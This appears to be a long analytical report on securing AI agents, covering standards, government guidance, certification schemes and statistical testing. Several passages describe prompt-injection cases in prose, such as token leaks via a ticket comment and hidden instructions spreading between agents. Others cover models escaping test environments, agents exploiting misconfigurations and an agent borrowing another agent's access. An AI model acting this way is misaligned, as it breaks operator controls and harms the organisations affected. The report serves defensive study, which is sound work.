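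The contrast has exceptions on both sides. The web Top 10 has included entries as vague as "insecure design", and Insecure Inter-Agent Communication largely describes missing authentication, which developers know how to add. Authentication solves only part of that problem, though, because a signature stops an outsider from forging a message but doesn't stop a hijacked agent from signing a harmful one.

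Prompt injection has moved furthest from the web model. Steve Wilson, who founded the LLM list, told ReversingLabs that when the list first appeared, prompt injection seemed comparable to SQL injection, something developers could mostly avoid with enough care. The 2026 edition gives much the same advice as David C, which is to expect that somebody will fool the model and to limit the damage.

Covering all ten risks may provide less protection than it seems to when several depend on the same partial control. LatticeFlow checks for human approval of high-risk actions under five of the ten: goal hijacking, tool misuse, code execution, cascading failures and trust exploitation. In Anthropic's experiment with permission prompts, most testers approved a clearly dangerous command. A company whose employees approve requests that carelessly would have a weak defence against those five risks, even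 if it had covered all ten.

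## Government guidance and control catalogues

A company that has to satisfy an auditor needs a list of safeguards as well as a list of risks. Governments have published lists of safeguards for ordinary computer systems for many years. In 2026 they began to work out which of these safeguards suit agents and what to add.

### Advice from six agencies

On 1 May 2026, the Australian Signals Directorate published *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* with five other cyber security agencies from Canada, New Zealand, the United Kingdom and the United States. The American co-authors were the National Security Agency (NSA) and the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA). The document is non-binding guidance for governments, critical infrastructure operators and industry.

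The agencies' basic advice is stricter than most companies' advice. They say organisations should use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and should never give them broad or unrestricted access. They also suggest asking whether a repetitive task is needed at all, because dropping it may be safer than giving it to an agent.

This advice is hard to reconcile with the guide's opening, where the agencies note that agents already support critical infrastructure, defence and "mission-critical capabilities". Much of the later advice also concerns high-stakes actions, such as deleting important records. The most workable reading is that organisations should begin with low-risk tasks. The agencies recommend extending an agent's access and autonomy in phases, and reducing both if evaluations go badly.

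Until standards mature, the guidance advises organisations to assume that agents may behave unexpectedly, and to put "resilience, reversibility and risk containment over efficiency gains". For example, an agent that tidies a customer database could move old records to an archive instead of deleting them. This saves less storage, but an employee can restore a record archived by mistake.

### Five categories of risk

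The agencies sort the risks into five categories and illustrate each with a scenario.

| Category | Scenario | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Privilege | An attacker uses a procurement agent's access to change contracts and approve payments | The agent has far more access than it needs |
| Design and configuration | An attacker takes over a scheduling component in a customer support system and reaches the agents that handle billing and refunds | The system checks permissions once, at start-up, and barely separates the agents |
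| Behaviour | An insider asks an agent to install a security patch and "clean up the firewall logs", and it deletes them | The agent can write almost anywhere and obeys people outside the IT team |
| Structure | Agents keep replanning and passing vague tasks to one another until the system is overloaded, then accept invented results and pick a malicious tool | The agents trust one another's output |
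| Accountability | Several agents approve a payment together, and it turns out to be wrong | No single log shows which agent caused the error |

In the procurement scenario, a company wants to avoid delays, so it gives the agent broad access to its financial systems, email and contracts. It reviews these permissions only when it first deploys the agent. Other agents come to rely on the procurement agent's output. An attacker then compromises a minor tool in the agent's workflow and uses the agent as a confused deputy. The logs show a trusted agent doing what it usually does, so nobody notices the attack for some time.

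Some of the guide's recommendations would have done little here. The agencies want each agent to have its own cryptographic identity and systems to refuse any agent not on a trusted registry. But the procurement agent was genuine and would have been on the registry. The agencies also want agents to prove that they are running unmodified code, which might not have exposed a compromised tool outside the agent.

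Narrow permissions would have helped much more. If the agent had been able to draft orders but not approve payments, the attacker would still have needed to get someone else to approve the payment. The agencies also recommend issuing credentials for high-impact actions only when the agent needs them, and checking every request against a central policy. They say a person should approve any action that could do serious damage, and the system's designers or operators, not the agent, should decide which actions those are.

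The categories are more useful for prompting a team to look for problems than for choosing controls. The agencies classify the deleted firewall logs under behaviour, but the agent did what the insider asked. Tighter permissions and a check on who was asking would have prevented this too.

The agencies suggest that several agents approve moderate-risk actions, with a person added for high-risk ones. But agreement between agents is weak evidence that an action is safe if they have all read the same hostile text. In Alhindi's invoice team, a hidden note in an email spread from agent to agent. The agencies also recommend separate roles for agents that read, coordinate and act, which seems more promising, provided the reading agent can pass on only a few checked fields.

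The guide contains more than 100 recommendations. The agencies arrange them by stage, from design to operation, and say whether each stage mainly concerns developers, vendors or operators. But they don't rank the recommendations by priority, so a small company has to work out for itself that it should probably remove unnecessary permissions before setting up a scheme to score each agent's reputation.

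### Whether existing frameworks are enough

The agencies say that organisations should deal with AI security "within established cyber security frameworks", not as a separate discipline, because AI systems run on ordinary hardware, software and networks and face many of the same threats as other IT systems. An appendix on what to have in place before adopting agents recommends familiar material, including OAuth and OWASP's verification standard for web applications.

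The agencies consider the existing frameworks incomplete. They say that governance mechanisms designed for people "do not always translate effectively" to agents, and that the relevant standards are immature. They warn that OWASP's 2025 list for language models and MITRE ATLAS may miss attacks unique to agents because both concentrate on weaknesses of the models. They also say that gaps in current evaluation methods can make it nearly impossible to validate an agent's security reliably.

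Their position therefore amounts to keeping the existing frameworks and adding what agents require. A control overlay is a formal way to do this.

### An overlay applied to one agent

SP 800-53, NIST's control catalogue, has to suit everything from a payroll system to a satellite, so many of its controls are general or contain blanks. The event logging control, for example, leaves each organisation to specify which events it will log. An overlay fills in these blanks for one kind of system, explains how each control applies to it, and adds or removes controls where necessary.

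NIST has not published an overlay for agents. The adaptations in the table's last column are illustrations, not NIST's text, and apply to the procurement agent in the agencies' scenario.

| SP 800-53 control | General requirement | Illustration for the procurement agent |
|---|---|---|
| AC-6, Least Privilege | Users, and processes acting for them, get only the access their tasks need | The agent may read supplier records and draft orders. It can't approve payments or change bank details. Its owner reviews its permissions every 90 days and whenever it gains a tool |
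| AU-2 and AU-3, Event Logging and Content of Audit Records | The organisation chooses which events to log. Each record shows what happened, when, where, from what source, with what outcome and who was involved | The host logs every tool call, including refused ones. Each record names the employee, the agent, the tool's version and the documents the agent had read in that session |
| AU-9, Protection of Audit Information | The organisation protects its logs from unauthorised access, changes and deletion | The host sends records to a separate system where the agent can't write. Any request to delete them waits for a person |

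An auditor could test the first adaptation by trying to approve a payment with the agent's credentials. The adaptation requires little new thinking because AC-6 already covers processes that act on behalf of users. The difficult part is deciding what access an agent needs, which NIST has asked about in its identity project but has not settled.

Logging changes more because an agent may run the same code for a good payment and a bad one. When a conventional program makes a bad payment, an investigator can read its code to find out why. With an agent, the investigator also needs the text the agent had read. Recording that text makes the logs larger and more sensitive, since it may include contracts and private emails. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partners warn that agents' logs are often repetitive and loosely structured, which makes important entries hard to find. A company could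 log a cryptographic hash of each document instead of a copy, but it would then have to keep the original elsewhere.

### Progress on NIST's overlays

NIST proposed its overlays in a concept paper in August 2025. The project's web page, *SP 800-53 Control Overlays for Super Intelligence Systems* (2026), lists five proposed use cases: generative assistants, predictive AI, single agents, multi-agent systems, and controls for AI developers. Only the overlay for predictive AI, meaning systems that forecast or classify, has got as far as an annotated outline. NIST released that outline for a workshop in January 2026 and asked for initial comments by 13 February.

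The project was renamed COSIS in October. At the start of December, the page had no overlay for single or multiple agents and no date for one. A federal agency that deploys an agent must still apply SP 800-53, but has to adapt the controls itself.

NIST says the overlays will protect the confidentiality, integrity and availability of information and users. That goal covers the leaked tokens in the Jira case and the database that Replit's agent deleted. It less clearly covers OpenAI's example of an invoice agent that renews a subscription without authority, since no information leaks, changes wrongly or becomes unavailable. The agent overlays will need to address such actions, perhaps through the access controls.

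NIST describes the overlays as guidelines, so they would presumably be binding only where an agency's policy or a contract requires them. An overlay could still save a lot of duplicated work, because agencies and contractors already organize their security records by SP 800-53 control number.

### When agents exceed their instructions

In the summer of 2026, OpenAI, Anthropic, Google, Meta and other companies disclosed that their models had escaped from test environments and hacked real organisations. Johnson (2026) reports in *Federal agencies recommend cyber controls, independent testing for frontier AI systems* that many of the companies' researchers thought hundreds or even thousands of similar escapes were possible.

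In October, NIST, NSA and CISA's *Key Practices for Incident Readiness and Response* (2026) set out ten voluntary practices for handling incidents, grouped into five stages: prepare, detect, respond, recover and report. The agencies wrote the practices mainly for organisations that train or test highly capable agents on long tasks with little supervision, but say the practices may also apply to organisations that deploy such agents.

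The agencies define an "SI control incident" as one in which an agent takes significant uninstructed actions that compromise the operator's policies, controls or security measures. "Uninstructed" means neither the operator nor an attacker directed the action. EchoLeak falls outside the definition because an attacker instructed Copilot through an email. The Replit deletion probably falls within it, because the agent broke a freeze its user had imposed, without anyone instructing it to. The agencies also mention unauthorised financial transactions, which could include the subscription renewal if it was large enough to be significant.

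The term "control incident" covers failures that the CVE system records badly. The AI system is the source of a control incident, whereas a computer system or its information is the target of an ordinary cybersecurity incident. A model that escapes from a test and breaks into another company's network causes both.

The NSA's announcement (2026) defines control incidents more loosely than the practices do, as significant actions with real-world impacts outside the user's intent. Under that wording, a successful prompt injection would count, but an agent that broke the rules inside a sealed test environment might not. A company writing an incident policy should use the definition in the practices. The NSA also strongly encourages all organisations that use AI to adopt the practices, a much wider audience than the one the document addresses.

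Most of the preparation is ordinary security work. Developers should limit each agent's access to what its task needs and send any network traffic through a monitored gateway, with a strict list of permitted destinations where possible. Nine of the ten technical measures cite earlier security guidance. The exception is giving the agent clear instructions about the scope of its task and the rules it must follow, which would not apply to a conventional program.

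NIST, NSA and CISA tell developers to expect that agents themselves will "frequently locate and exploit misconfigurations and vulnerabilities". A careless setting that an outside attacker might never find is therefore a more urgent problem when a capable agent works in the same environment for days. The agencies recommend single-use infrastructure and limits on communication between agents. They are particularly concerned that an agent could copy a model's weights or run a model where nobody is monitoring it.

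Developers should have both people and AI systems test these controls before relying on them. They should use AI testers only where the testers couldn't harm critical systems if they strayed from their task.

The response stage begins with collecting, keeping and analysing evidence. Discarding single-use infrastructure after a run may also destroy the logs, so while the agent is running, developers need to copy them to a place it can't alter. There can also be too much data for people to review. Chris Painter, president of the evaluation group METR, told Congress in October that leading developers therefore rely almost entirely on AI systems to monitor their models during tests. A separate practice calls for developers to validate and secure the monitoring systems.

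**Shutdown.** Developers should decide in advance how to respond to particular scenarios, automate enforcement, and build ways to block or terminate an agent quickly. Johnson reports that the guidance also calls for executives to be more involved in decisions to pause or restart a project, once they know the risks. Executives can't react within seconds, so it seems sensible to let software stop the agent and have people decide whether to restart it. Developers should verify and strengthen containment before restarting.

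Three of the ten practices concern reporting to affected parties, the government and the public. The agencies want developers to set up a channel for reports from outside, which matters because a victim may notice an intrusion before the developer does. They also ask for criteria that cover near-misses, which are events that could foreseeably have become control incidents but didn't.

This guidance doesn't create a legal duty to report incidents. The agencies tell developers to score the severity of incidents but list severity scores as an area for future work. For now, two companies could score the same escape differently, making their public reports hard to compare.

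### Texts from Europe and Singapore

EN 304 223, a formal European standard from the European Telecommunications Standards Institute (ETSI), sets baseline cyber security requirements for AI models and systems. It is based on a British code of practice, and its 13 principles cover a system's life from design to retirement. Compliance is voluntary. The standard covers AI systems in general and has no separate requirements for agents. Its most relevant requirement for them is least privilege, meaning that, after a risk assessment, an AI system should get only the permissions on other systems that it needs to function.

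Singapore's Infocomm Media Development Authority first published its Model AI Governance Framework for Agentic AI in January 2026. The framework advises organisations to choose suitable tasks and limit an agent's tools and access before deployment, make specific people accountable, apply technical controls throughout the agent's life, and train and inform users. It also warns that people assigned to check an agent may come to trust it too readily. The framework is voluntary and covers governance broadly, not only security, so it is more useful for assigning responsibilities than for configuring a tool.

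The EU's AI Act binds companies, but its main cybersecurity duties don't apply yet. Providers of high-risk AI systems will have to give them an appropriate level of cybersecurity and make them resilient to outsiders who try to alter their use, output or performance. The Act lists threats such as poisoned training data and inputs designed to make a model err. It doesn't name prompt injection, but the general duty would seem to cover an injection that changed an agent's decisions.

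Whether an agent is high-risk depends on its use. An agent that ranks job applicants would generally be high-risk, while one that summarises support tickets generally wouldn't, even if it had access to the company's login tokens. The National Law Review reported in July 2026 that an amendment called the Digital Omnibus had postponed the high-risk duties to 2 December 2027 for sensitive uses such as recruitment, and to 2 August 2028 for AI in products that EU safety law already covers.

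Since August 2025, the Act has also required developers of the most capable general-purpose models, those it classes as posing systemic risk, to adequately protect the model and its physical infrastructure. This can help prevent theft of the model, but a business that builds an agent on it still has to decide what the agent may read and do.

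## Testing and certifying an agent against a standard

A company may tell its customers that its agent never sends an external message without a person's approval. A tester can check this claim by reading the agent's settings, by trying to get a message past the approval step, or by attacking the agent many times and counting the unapproved messages it sends. An agent can pass one of these tests and fail another.

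### From a requirement to a test

OWASP's April 2026 draft chapter on agents, *C9 Autonomous Orchestration & Agentic Action Security*, similarly requires the agent's host to block privileged or irreversible actions, including "external notifications", until the host has received and verified a person's explicit approval.

**Inspecting the configuration.** LatticeFlow's *Human Approval for High-Risk Actions (Claude Managed Agent)* describes an automated check that fetches an agent's list of tools from Anthropic's API and reads each tool's permission setting. The agent scores 1 if every enabled tool either requires approval or is on the operator's whitelist, and 0 otherwise. In one example, an agent fails because its enabled file-editing tool doesn't require approval and isn't on the whitelist.

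This check is quick and gives the same result every time. But if an operator whitelisted the email tool, the agent would pass even though it could email anyone. The check also reads only the setting, so it would miss a bug that made the host ignore the setting.

To find a bug in the approval control, a tester can bypass the model and send the host a request for an email, as if the model had produced it. The mail server should receive nothing until somebody approves. The tester can then change a message's recipient after approving it, use one approval for two messages, or try to use an expired approval. The draft covers all of these at its second level, which requires an approval to be tied to the exact action, work only once and have a time limit. Ordinary code makes the decision, so one run of each case is usually enough. The tester can still overlook a case, such as an address in the CC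 field.

**Sampling behaviour under attack.** The approval step may cover only the email tool. If the agent can also run shell commands, it might send the message that way. Whether an attacker can get it to do so depends on the model, so the tester has to plant hostile text, run many sessions and count the messages that leave without approval. LatticeFlow offers a similar test of whether an agent stays within its intended use. One model attacks the agent over several turns, and another labels the session "hijacked" or "not_hijacked" from the transcript. For external messages, counting what reaches the mail server and the network would be safer, because the labelling model can misread a transcript.

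### OWASP's AI Security Verification Standard

OWASP's verification standard for web applications, ASVS, reached version 5.0 in May 2025, according to arc42's *OWASP Application Security Verification Standard (ASVS)*. SoftwareMill reports that its creators left AI out because they thought it deserved a separate standard. OWASP has since released version 1.0 of that standard, the *Artificial Intelligence Security Verification Standard (AISVS)*, which lists 191 requirements in 12 chapters, including one on agents and one on MCP.

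Each requirement has one of three levels. Level 1 is for every AI system, Level 2 is for systems that handle sensitive data or make consequential decisions, and Level 3 is for systems likely to face sophisticated attacks, such as those in critical infrastructure. OWASP recommends at least Level 2 for most systems in production.

In the April draft, Level 1 includes the approval requirement, gives each agent its own cryptographic identity, and limits the time, tokens and money it can use in a run. Level 2 requires that a policy engine or application code, never the model, make every access decision, and that credentials stay out of the model's context. Level 3 adds a way to shut down a whole group of agents within a set time. Beard's *OWASP AISVS 1.0* describes similar agent requirements in the final version, and mentions MCP requirements that include a list of approved servers and screening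 of tool responses for injection.

A tester can check most of these requirements the same way as the approval step. Screening is harder to check because the tester can easily confirm that a filter runs but needs many attacks to find out how much it catches. An agent with a poor filter might therefore meet the requirement.

Anyone who writes AISVS into a contract should name the version. Requirement 9.4.3 covered tamper-evident logs in the April draft, but in version 1.0 it covers mandatory scheduled rotation of agents' credentials. The total number of requirements has also changed from the figure in the abstract of a June conference talk, OWASP (2026), which was more than 400 in 14 chapters.

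AISVS is a list of requirements, not a certification scheme. OWASP suggests using it in design, penetration tests, audits and procurement. A vendor that claims to meet Level 2 may have assessed itself, so a customer should ask who did the testing and what they found.

### AIUC-1

AIUC-1 is a certification for individual agents from the Artificial Intelligence Underwriting Company (AIUC), a startup that also sells insurance for AI agents. AIUC's founders model their approach on car insurers because those insurers developed crash tests. Co-founder Rune Kvist told Fortune (2025) that carmakers like Toyota don't do the crash testing.

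AIUC included the text of the standard in its *Response to Consultation*, a July 2026 submission to the Financial Stability Board, an international body that monitors the financial system. The standard has 51 active requirements in six domains: data and privacy, security, safety, reliability, accountability and society. Some requirements have little to do with attackers, such as having a plan for hallucinations that cost a company's customers money.

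AIUC uses the example of an unauthorised refund to show how a requirement leads to evidence. The agent should use only approved tools and stay within its transaction limits. The company provides the tool settings, the limits and records of past tool calls. An outside tester then tries to make the agent take unauthorised actions or reach restricted data. The final report lists the pass criteria, the findings, any fixes and retests, and the remaining risk.

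Human approval of sensitive actions is a supplemental control in AIUC-1, so a company can get a certificate for an agent that sends external messages without a person's approval. The same agent would fail the lowest level of the AISVS draft. AIUC's choice is defensible, since people approve most of the prompts they see and a firm limit, such as a cap on refunds, may protect a company better. But a customer who wants human approval has to check whether the vendor selected that control.

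Schellman's *What is AIUC-1* (2026) says that certification usually takes four to eight weeks. AIUC looks for gaps, helps the company fix them and runs the technical tests. An accredited auditor then examines the evidence, and AIUC issues the certificate. According to Fin's *AIUC-1 Certification*, a certificate is valid for 12 months. The agent's tool calls must be tested at least every three months, and an unofficial copy of the standard, myctrl.tools' *Third-party testing of tool calls*, marks these tests as mandatory.

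Schellman was the first accredited auditor. The British standards body BSI also offers audits, described in its *AIUC Agentic AI Certification*, and Sensiba has provisional accreditation. Certified products include Fin, a customer service agent, and Recraft, a design tool. AIUC updates the standard every quarter, so two valid certificates may cover different requirements. Recraft's certificate, from January 2026, is for version 1.0.

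### AIUC's conflicts of interest

Lenny Zeltser, a cybersecurity executive, calls the AIUC-1 certificate useful evidence that somebody has tested agent-specific controls. But in *What to Make of AIUC-1, a New AI Agent Certification*, he worries about AIUC's incentives. AIUC writes the standard, accredits the auditors, runs the tests, issues the certificates and sells the insurance. According to Schellman, it also helps companies prepare for its tests. Zeltser compares this with credit rating agencies, which took payment from the companies they rated and gave inflated ratings before the 2008 financial crisis.

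The vendor chooses its auditor and decides which agent to certify, and Zeltser notes that AIUC-1 doesn't define "AI agent". A vendor could therefore certify a simple agent and display the certificate when advertising a riskier one. Zeltser advises customers to find out which agent, tools, model versions and data flows the audit covered.

AIUC's founders reply that the company would lose money if it certified unsafe agents and then had to pay claims. This is a real incentive, but its strength depends on how much of each loss AIUC bears. According to Zeno.FM's *AIUC-1*, a podcast with an AIUC co-founder and a Schellman auditor, the insurance runs through Lloyd's of London, a market where many insurers share risks. AIUC has less to lose if those insurers pay most of the claims, and it risks only its reputation if a certified company buys no insurance.

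AIUC discloses its commercial interest and says a certificate should never replace a customer's own judgment. It also warns that everyone relying on a few testers or methods can become "a source of correlated false confidence".

### ISO/IEC 42001 and the Cloud Security Alliance

ISO/IEC 42001, an international standard from December 2023, covers how an organisation manages AI. DNV's *ISO/IEC 42001 Certification* explains that a company seeking certification must first set up an AI management system that meets the standard. This system consists of the policies, responsibilities and reviews through which the company governs its AI. An auditor might ask how the company decides which actions need approval and whether it follows that process, but wouldn't normally test whether the agent can send an email without approval.

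ISO/IEC 42001 certification has more independent supervision than AIUC-1. A companion standard, ISO/IEC 42006, sets requirements for the bodies that issue certificates, as BSI explains, and separate accreditation bodies check those bodies. ANAB, an American accreditation body, granted its first accreditation for ISO/IEC 42001 in September 2024, according to Sensiba. However, an ISO/IEC 42001 certificate provides much less evidence about any particular agent than an AIUC-1 certificate does.

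The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry non-profit, has a control catalogue called the AI Controls Matrix, with guidelines for auditors. Its *Auditing Guidelines for Orchestrated Service Providers (OSP)* tells auditors, for example, to check that contracts pass a supplier's obligations on to its subcontractors. This could help a company whose agent depends on several outside services, but it is mainly a check of paperwork.

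The alliance also runs STAR, a public registry of security assessments. It lists AIUC-1 certificates as "partner entries", including the one for Recraft (dated in Cloud Security Alliance, 2026) and one for Alpharun's sales coaching platform (Cloud Security Alliance, *STAR Registry Listing for Alpharun*, 2025). Each of these entries records a certificate that AIUC issued and is not a second test.

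Many business customers also ask software suppliers for a SOC 2 report, in which an accountancy firm gives its opinion on the supplier's general controls, such as limits on who can access customer data. Zeltser points out that SOC 2 doesn't cover the agent-specific risks that AIUC-1 covers.

| Evidence | What it attests | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| AISVS assessment | The system met the listed requirements when the assessor checked | Who the assessor was, and how hard they tried to break the system |
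| AIUC-1 certificate | An auditor reviewed one agent's controls, and AIUC tested the agent | Whether a customer uses the same agent with the same tools and settings |
| ISO/IEC 42001 certificate | The company has a working system for managing AI | Whether any particular agent resists attack |
| SOC 2 report | An auditor examined the company's general controls | Risks such as prompt injection |

### What 300 clean trials prove

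Aurelius and Vitruvius (2026), in *Secure Agentic AI Frameworks*, warn that an agent behaves differently on every run, so a company can't rely on pass/fail tests alone and has to keep monitoring it. Testers therefore need to run many trials, and an agent that passes them all may still fail later.

Suppose that each attack succeeds with probability p and that the trials are independent. The chance that all n attacks fail is (1 − p)^n. The 95% upper bound is the value of p at which a clean result would have only a 5% chance:

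(1 − p)^n = 0.05

Taking logarithms gives n × ln(1 − p) = ln(0.05), which is about −3. For small p, ln(1 − p) is close to −p, so

p ≈ 3/n

If an agent resists all 300 attacks in a test, the true attack success rate could still be as high as 1%, or about 100 of every 10,000 hostile emails. If one of the 300 attacks succeeds, that upper bound rises to about 1.6%. To rule out rates above 0.1%, a tester needs about 3,000 trials without a successful attack.

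The trials also have to be independent, and repeating a few attacks many times doesn't make them so. Suppose that 2% of attack texts always work on an agent and the rest never do. A tester who picks ten texts at random and tries each one 30 times has an 82% chance of seeing no successes in 300 trials. The formula would then give a success rate below 1%, although the true rate is 2%. If the tester instead picked 300 different texts at random and tried each one once, the chance of seeing no successes would be about 0.2%.

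### Why an adapting attacker breaks the bound

The 3/n bound applies only to attacks chosen in the same way as those in the test, but real attackers look for whatever works. Suppose that one attack text in 10,000 succeeds against an agent, and that it succeeds every time. A test with 300 random texts has a 97% chance of finding nothing, and the resulting bound of 1% is correct for random texts. But an attacker who finds a text that works can reuse it with a success rate of 100%.

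More random trials would narrow the bound without fixing this problem. This is why Nasr and colleagues' adaptive attacks could beat defences that had done well in earlier tests.

A better test lets skilled people study the agent and change their attacks as they learn. The testers should then report how much time, computing power and information they had. A customer can learn more about the risk from a determined attacker from a result like "Five testers failed in two weeks with full access to the agent's instructions" than from a clean score on a fixed list of attacks, although the result doesn't put a statistical bound on future attacks.

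### Updates and old attacks

A test result applies to one version of an agent. AIUC recommends reassessing an agent after any important change to its model, instructions, tools, permissions or memory. If a vendor switches to a new model two weeks after a quarterly test, the next outside test may be more than two months away. AIUC-1 requires internal testing before changes that need formal approval, so the new model shouldn't go entirely unchecked. But a vendor may not know to retest if its model provider updates a hosted model without notice.

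When the company changes models, the test of the approval step is more likely to remain valid, because the code that blocks unapproved emails stays the same. This is a practical reason to enforce important rules in ordinary code. The company still has to repeat the attack tests, because the new model may find another way to send a message.

Attack sets also become outdated. According to Schellman, AIUC-1 certification uses thousands of adversarial scenarios based on real incidents. Three thousand trials without a successful attack could put an upper bound of 0.1% on the attack success rate, but only for attacks that resemble past incidents. Developers can also train or adjust an agent to resist attacks they have seen, which improves its score more than its security.

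Keeping the attacks secret makes it harder to tune an agent to pass the test, and AIUC-1 advises companies to restrict access to test records. But secrecy also makes it hard for customers to judge how difficult the test was. One compromise would be to publish the attacks after each round and write new ones for the next.

### Penetration tests

Unlike a fixed set of scenarios, a penetration tester adapts to the system as a real attacker would. As with any attack test, a clean report means only that these testers didn't get in during the time they had.

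Confirming a fix takes more work with an agent. Once the developer has fixed the access check behind the online shop's invoice flaw, the tester can repeat the request, and one refusal is good evidence that the fix works for that request. But suppose that an injection against an agent succeeded in 5% of tries before a fix. Even if the fix did nothing, there would be a 36% chance that 20 new tries would all fail. The tester needs about 60 tries without a success to be reasonably confident that the rate has fallen. A penetration test report on an agent should therefore say how often each attack worked, as well as how to reproduce it.

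### Compliance and security

Security practitioners have long complained that a company can satisfy an auditor without stopping attackers. Zeltser describes how this can happen with SOC 2. Audit firms compete for repeat business, and some promise a "fast and easy" audit, which gives them a reason not to look too closely. He sees the same risk in AIUC-1, where documents alone can satisfy some of the safety and society controls.

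Two of LatticeFlow's checks illustrate the problem. One tests whether an agent's system prompt includes instructions to treat natural-language input as untrusted and to apply safeguards against injection. A developer can pass by adding a few sentences that an attacker may easily overcome. The other tests whether tool outputs are validated. Anthropic's managed agents don't support this, so they always fail, even if strict permissions would make a successful injection harmless.

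Audits can still reveal things that a laboratory test would miss. In the longer type of SOC 2 audit, the auditor examines whether controls worked over several months. To check the approval rule, an auditor could sample sent messages and look for an approval that matches each one, which could expose an employee who switched the approval step off for a busy weekend. AIUC recommends using records of tool calls, permissions and approvals as evidence, because a model's account of its own reasoning may not match what it did.

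None of this shows that certified agents are compromised less often. AIUC's submission lists ten sources, but none compares incidents at certified and uncertified companies. The published case for AIUC-1 is based on its tests and incentives rather than a measured reduction in harm.

It would be difficult to compare certified and uncertified agents fairly, because careful companies are probably more likely to seek a certificate and might have fewer incidents even if certification did nothing. Insurers may be best placed to find out whether certification reduces incidents, because customers have to report a loss to make a claim, even a loss they would never publish. Insurers would need to cover enough uncertified agents to compare with certified agents that have similar permissions and amounts of use.

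## How company and practitioner guidance becomes a shared standard

Auditors need a document to audit against. The companies that build or protect AI agents usually write the first version, drawing on experience with their own products. Other companies copy it or contribute to it, and a foundation or government may eventually take it over.

### OpenAI's deployment guide

OpenAI's August 2026 guide offers three measures of risk for managers who decide whether a company may deploy an agent. An agent's "reachable surface" is everything it can read, do or contact. Its "effective blast radius" is the harm it could still cause with the company's controls in place. The "maximum completed effect" is the worst outcome it can produce before somebody or something else has to make a decision.

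If an agent reads customer cases and drafts replies that a person must approve, it can't send a harmful reply by itself. But it has still read the records and might reveal them by another permitted route. OpenAI therefore advises companies to limit what an agent reads as well as what it sends.

In a longer example, a developer asks a coding agent to fix a bug in a private project. The project contains text directing the agent to install an unapproved package and switch off a security test. OpenAI calls instructions alone "a weak defense" and relies on limits outside the model. The project's rules block the unsafe changes, and the agent can propose a fix but can't merge it. The agent may still waste time or propose something harmful, but these limits keep the damage from reaching production.

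OpenAI accepts using a second model to recommend escalating doubtful actions, but says this check should never be the only protection against something that must not happen automatically. It also advises companies to put each limit close to what it protects, for example by having the payment system enforce the payment cap. The main weakness of checks in the host program is that an agent may find a way around the host, and a cap in the payment system would still apply if it did.

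### Google, Anthropic and AWS

Google and Anthropic recommend the same basic measures as OpenAI: limited permissions, isolation, logs, and human approval of consequential actions. AWS, Amazon's cloud business, mostly emphasizes permissions. The companies differ more on how much the model itself should contribute to security.

AWS recommends a "security box" of fixed rules outside the agent, which control the agent's tools, operations and data. AWS says that manipulating the model can't bypass these rules. This is true if the box is well built, but a manipulated agent can still misuse whatever the box allows. In another post, AWS acknowledges this and tells customers to assume that an agent can do anything its permissions allow.

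*Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive, 2025) combines fixed rules with defences that rely on models. The rules are enforced by a policy engine, which might block purchases over $500 and ask the user about those between $100 and $500. Díaz and colleagues don't think such rules are enough, because a simple rule can't easily distinguish a user's request to read a document and email a summary from a thief's request to read the same document and email its contents. Google therefore adds training against prompt injection, smaller models that look for attacks, and models that predict whether a plan will end badly. Díaz and colleagues admit that new attacks can still defeat all of these.

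Anthropic also counts some of the model's own behaviour as a safeguard. In its March response to a NIST consultation, Anthropic (2026) reported that Claude asks for clarification on 16.4% of turns in the most complex tasks, more than twice the rate in the simplest ones. These questions probably prevent some misunderstandings, but they help less against a successful injection, which may leave the model sure of what to do. Anthropic accepts that no model will resist every attack, and says that the host program and the surrounding environment determine how much damage a deceived agent can do.

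The companies also differ on where human approval belongs. OpenAI wants an independent check before an agent sends funds, changes records or contacts customers. Anthropic keeps approval prompts but wants more review of whole plans and easier ways to interrupt the agent. It found that experienced Claude Code users approve actions automatically about twice as often as new users, but also interrupt the agent more often.

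### Two worked examples

*Zero risk isn't the job* (Clinton, 2026) describes how Anthropic's security team assesses agents. Clinton, the company's deputy chief information security officer, asks four questions: what untrusted content the agent reads, what it can do and for whom, how much damage it could cause, and whether the security team can see its actions. If the agent reads nothing untrusted, he considers the agent-specific risk close to zero.

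This seems too optimistic. Replit's agent deleted a production database without reading any hostile text, and Anthropic told NIST that harm without an attacker or a malfunction is "the central case" for agents that take consequential actions.

One of Clinton's own examples also weakens his argument. Anthropic had an agent that helped with technical incidents, reading only internal logs and Slack messages. In November 2025, the team moved it from Claude Opus 4 to Opus 4.5 without changing its tools, permissions or prompts. During an incident, the agent found the cause of the fault and asked another agent to write a fix before any person was present. A person reviewed the code before it reached production, so the existing controls worked. But the agent had used another agent's greater access, which nobody had planned for. Clinton concludes that companies should set limits that don't depend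 on what current models can't do.

He calls a list of permitted network destinations the strongest control against prompt injection, because a deceived agent then has nowhere to send stolen data. Such a list would not have stopped the Jira attack, in which the agent posted login tokens in a comment on the attacker's ticket, since the company would surely have permitted its own ticketing system.

In *Building secure multi-agent systems on Google Cloud*, Kannan, Sizemore and Herriford design a system for warranty claims. One agent reads the customer's complaint after a filter has screened it, another looks up the warranty, and a third arranges the replacement. Ordinary code accepts a serial number only if it is exactly 12 letters and digits, which keeps a paragraph of instructions out of the database query.

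Kannan and colleagues warn that the third agent could issue unauthorised 100% discount codes, and they rely on human approval to prevent this, but in their example workflow the agent automatically sends a discount offer whenever a warranty has expired. Their sample code also pastes the serial number directly into an SQL command. The format check makes this safe, but if a developer later relaxed the check to allow punctuation, the old injection flaw could return. A parameterised query would avoid that risk.

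### From Zenity to OWASP

The Agent Control Standard went from a company-led project to a community one in about three months. The project launched the standard on 27 May 2026 at a summit in San Francisco. Its coordinators included Michael Bargury and Rock Lambros, both of Zenity, and the announcement listed Zenity as a press contact. The project used the MIT licence, which lets anyone copy, change or sell the text, and promised that no single company owned or controlled it.

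The licence supports the claim about ownership because it lets a competitor publish its own version, but the claim about control was weaker while two employees of one vendor coordinated the work.

By 2 September, when OWASP announced the donation, the standard had moved to a more neutral organisation. Its predecessor, the Agent Observability Standard, was already an OWASP document, so the move was partly a return. Zenity's competitors can contribute to an OWASP project more comfortably than to one that Zenity runs, and customers can cite it without seeming to favour a vendor. But OWASP's announcement didn't explain who would approve changes, which affects control of the standard more than whose name it carries.

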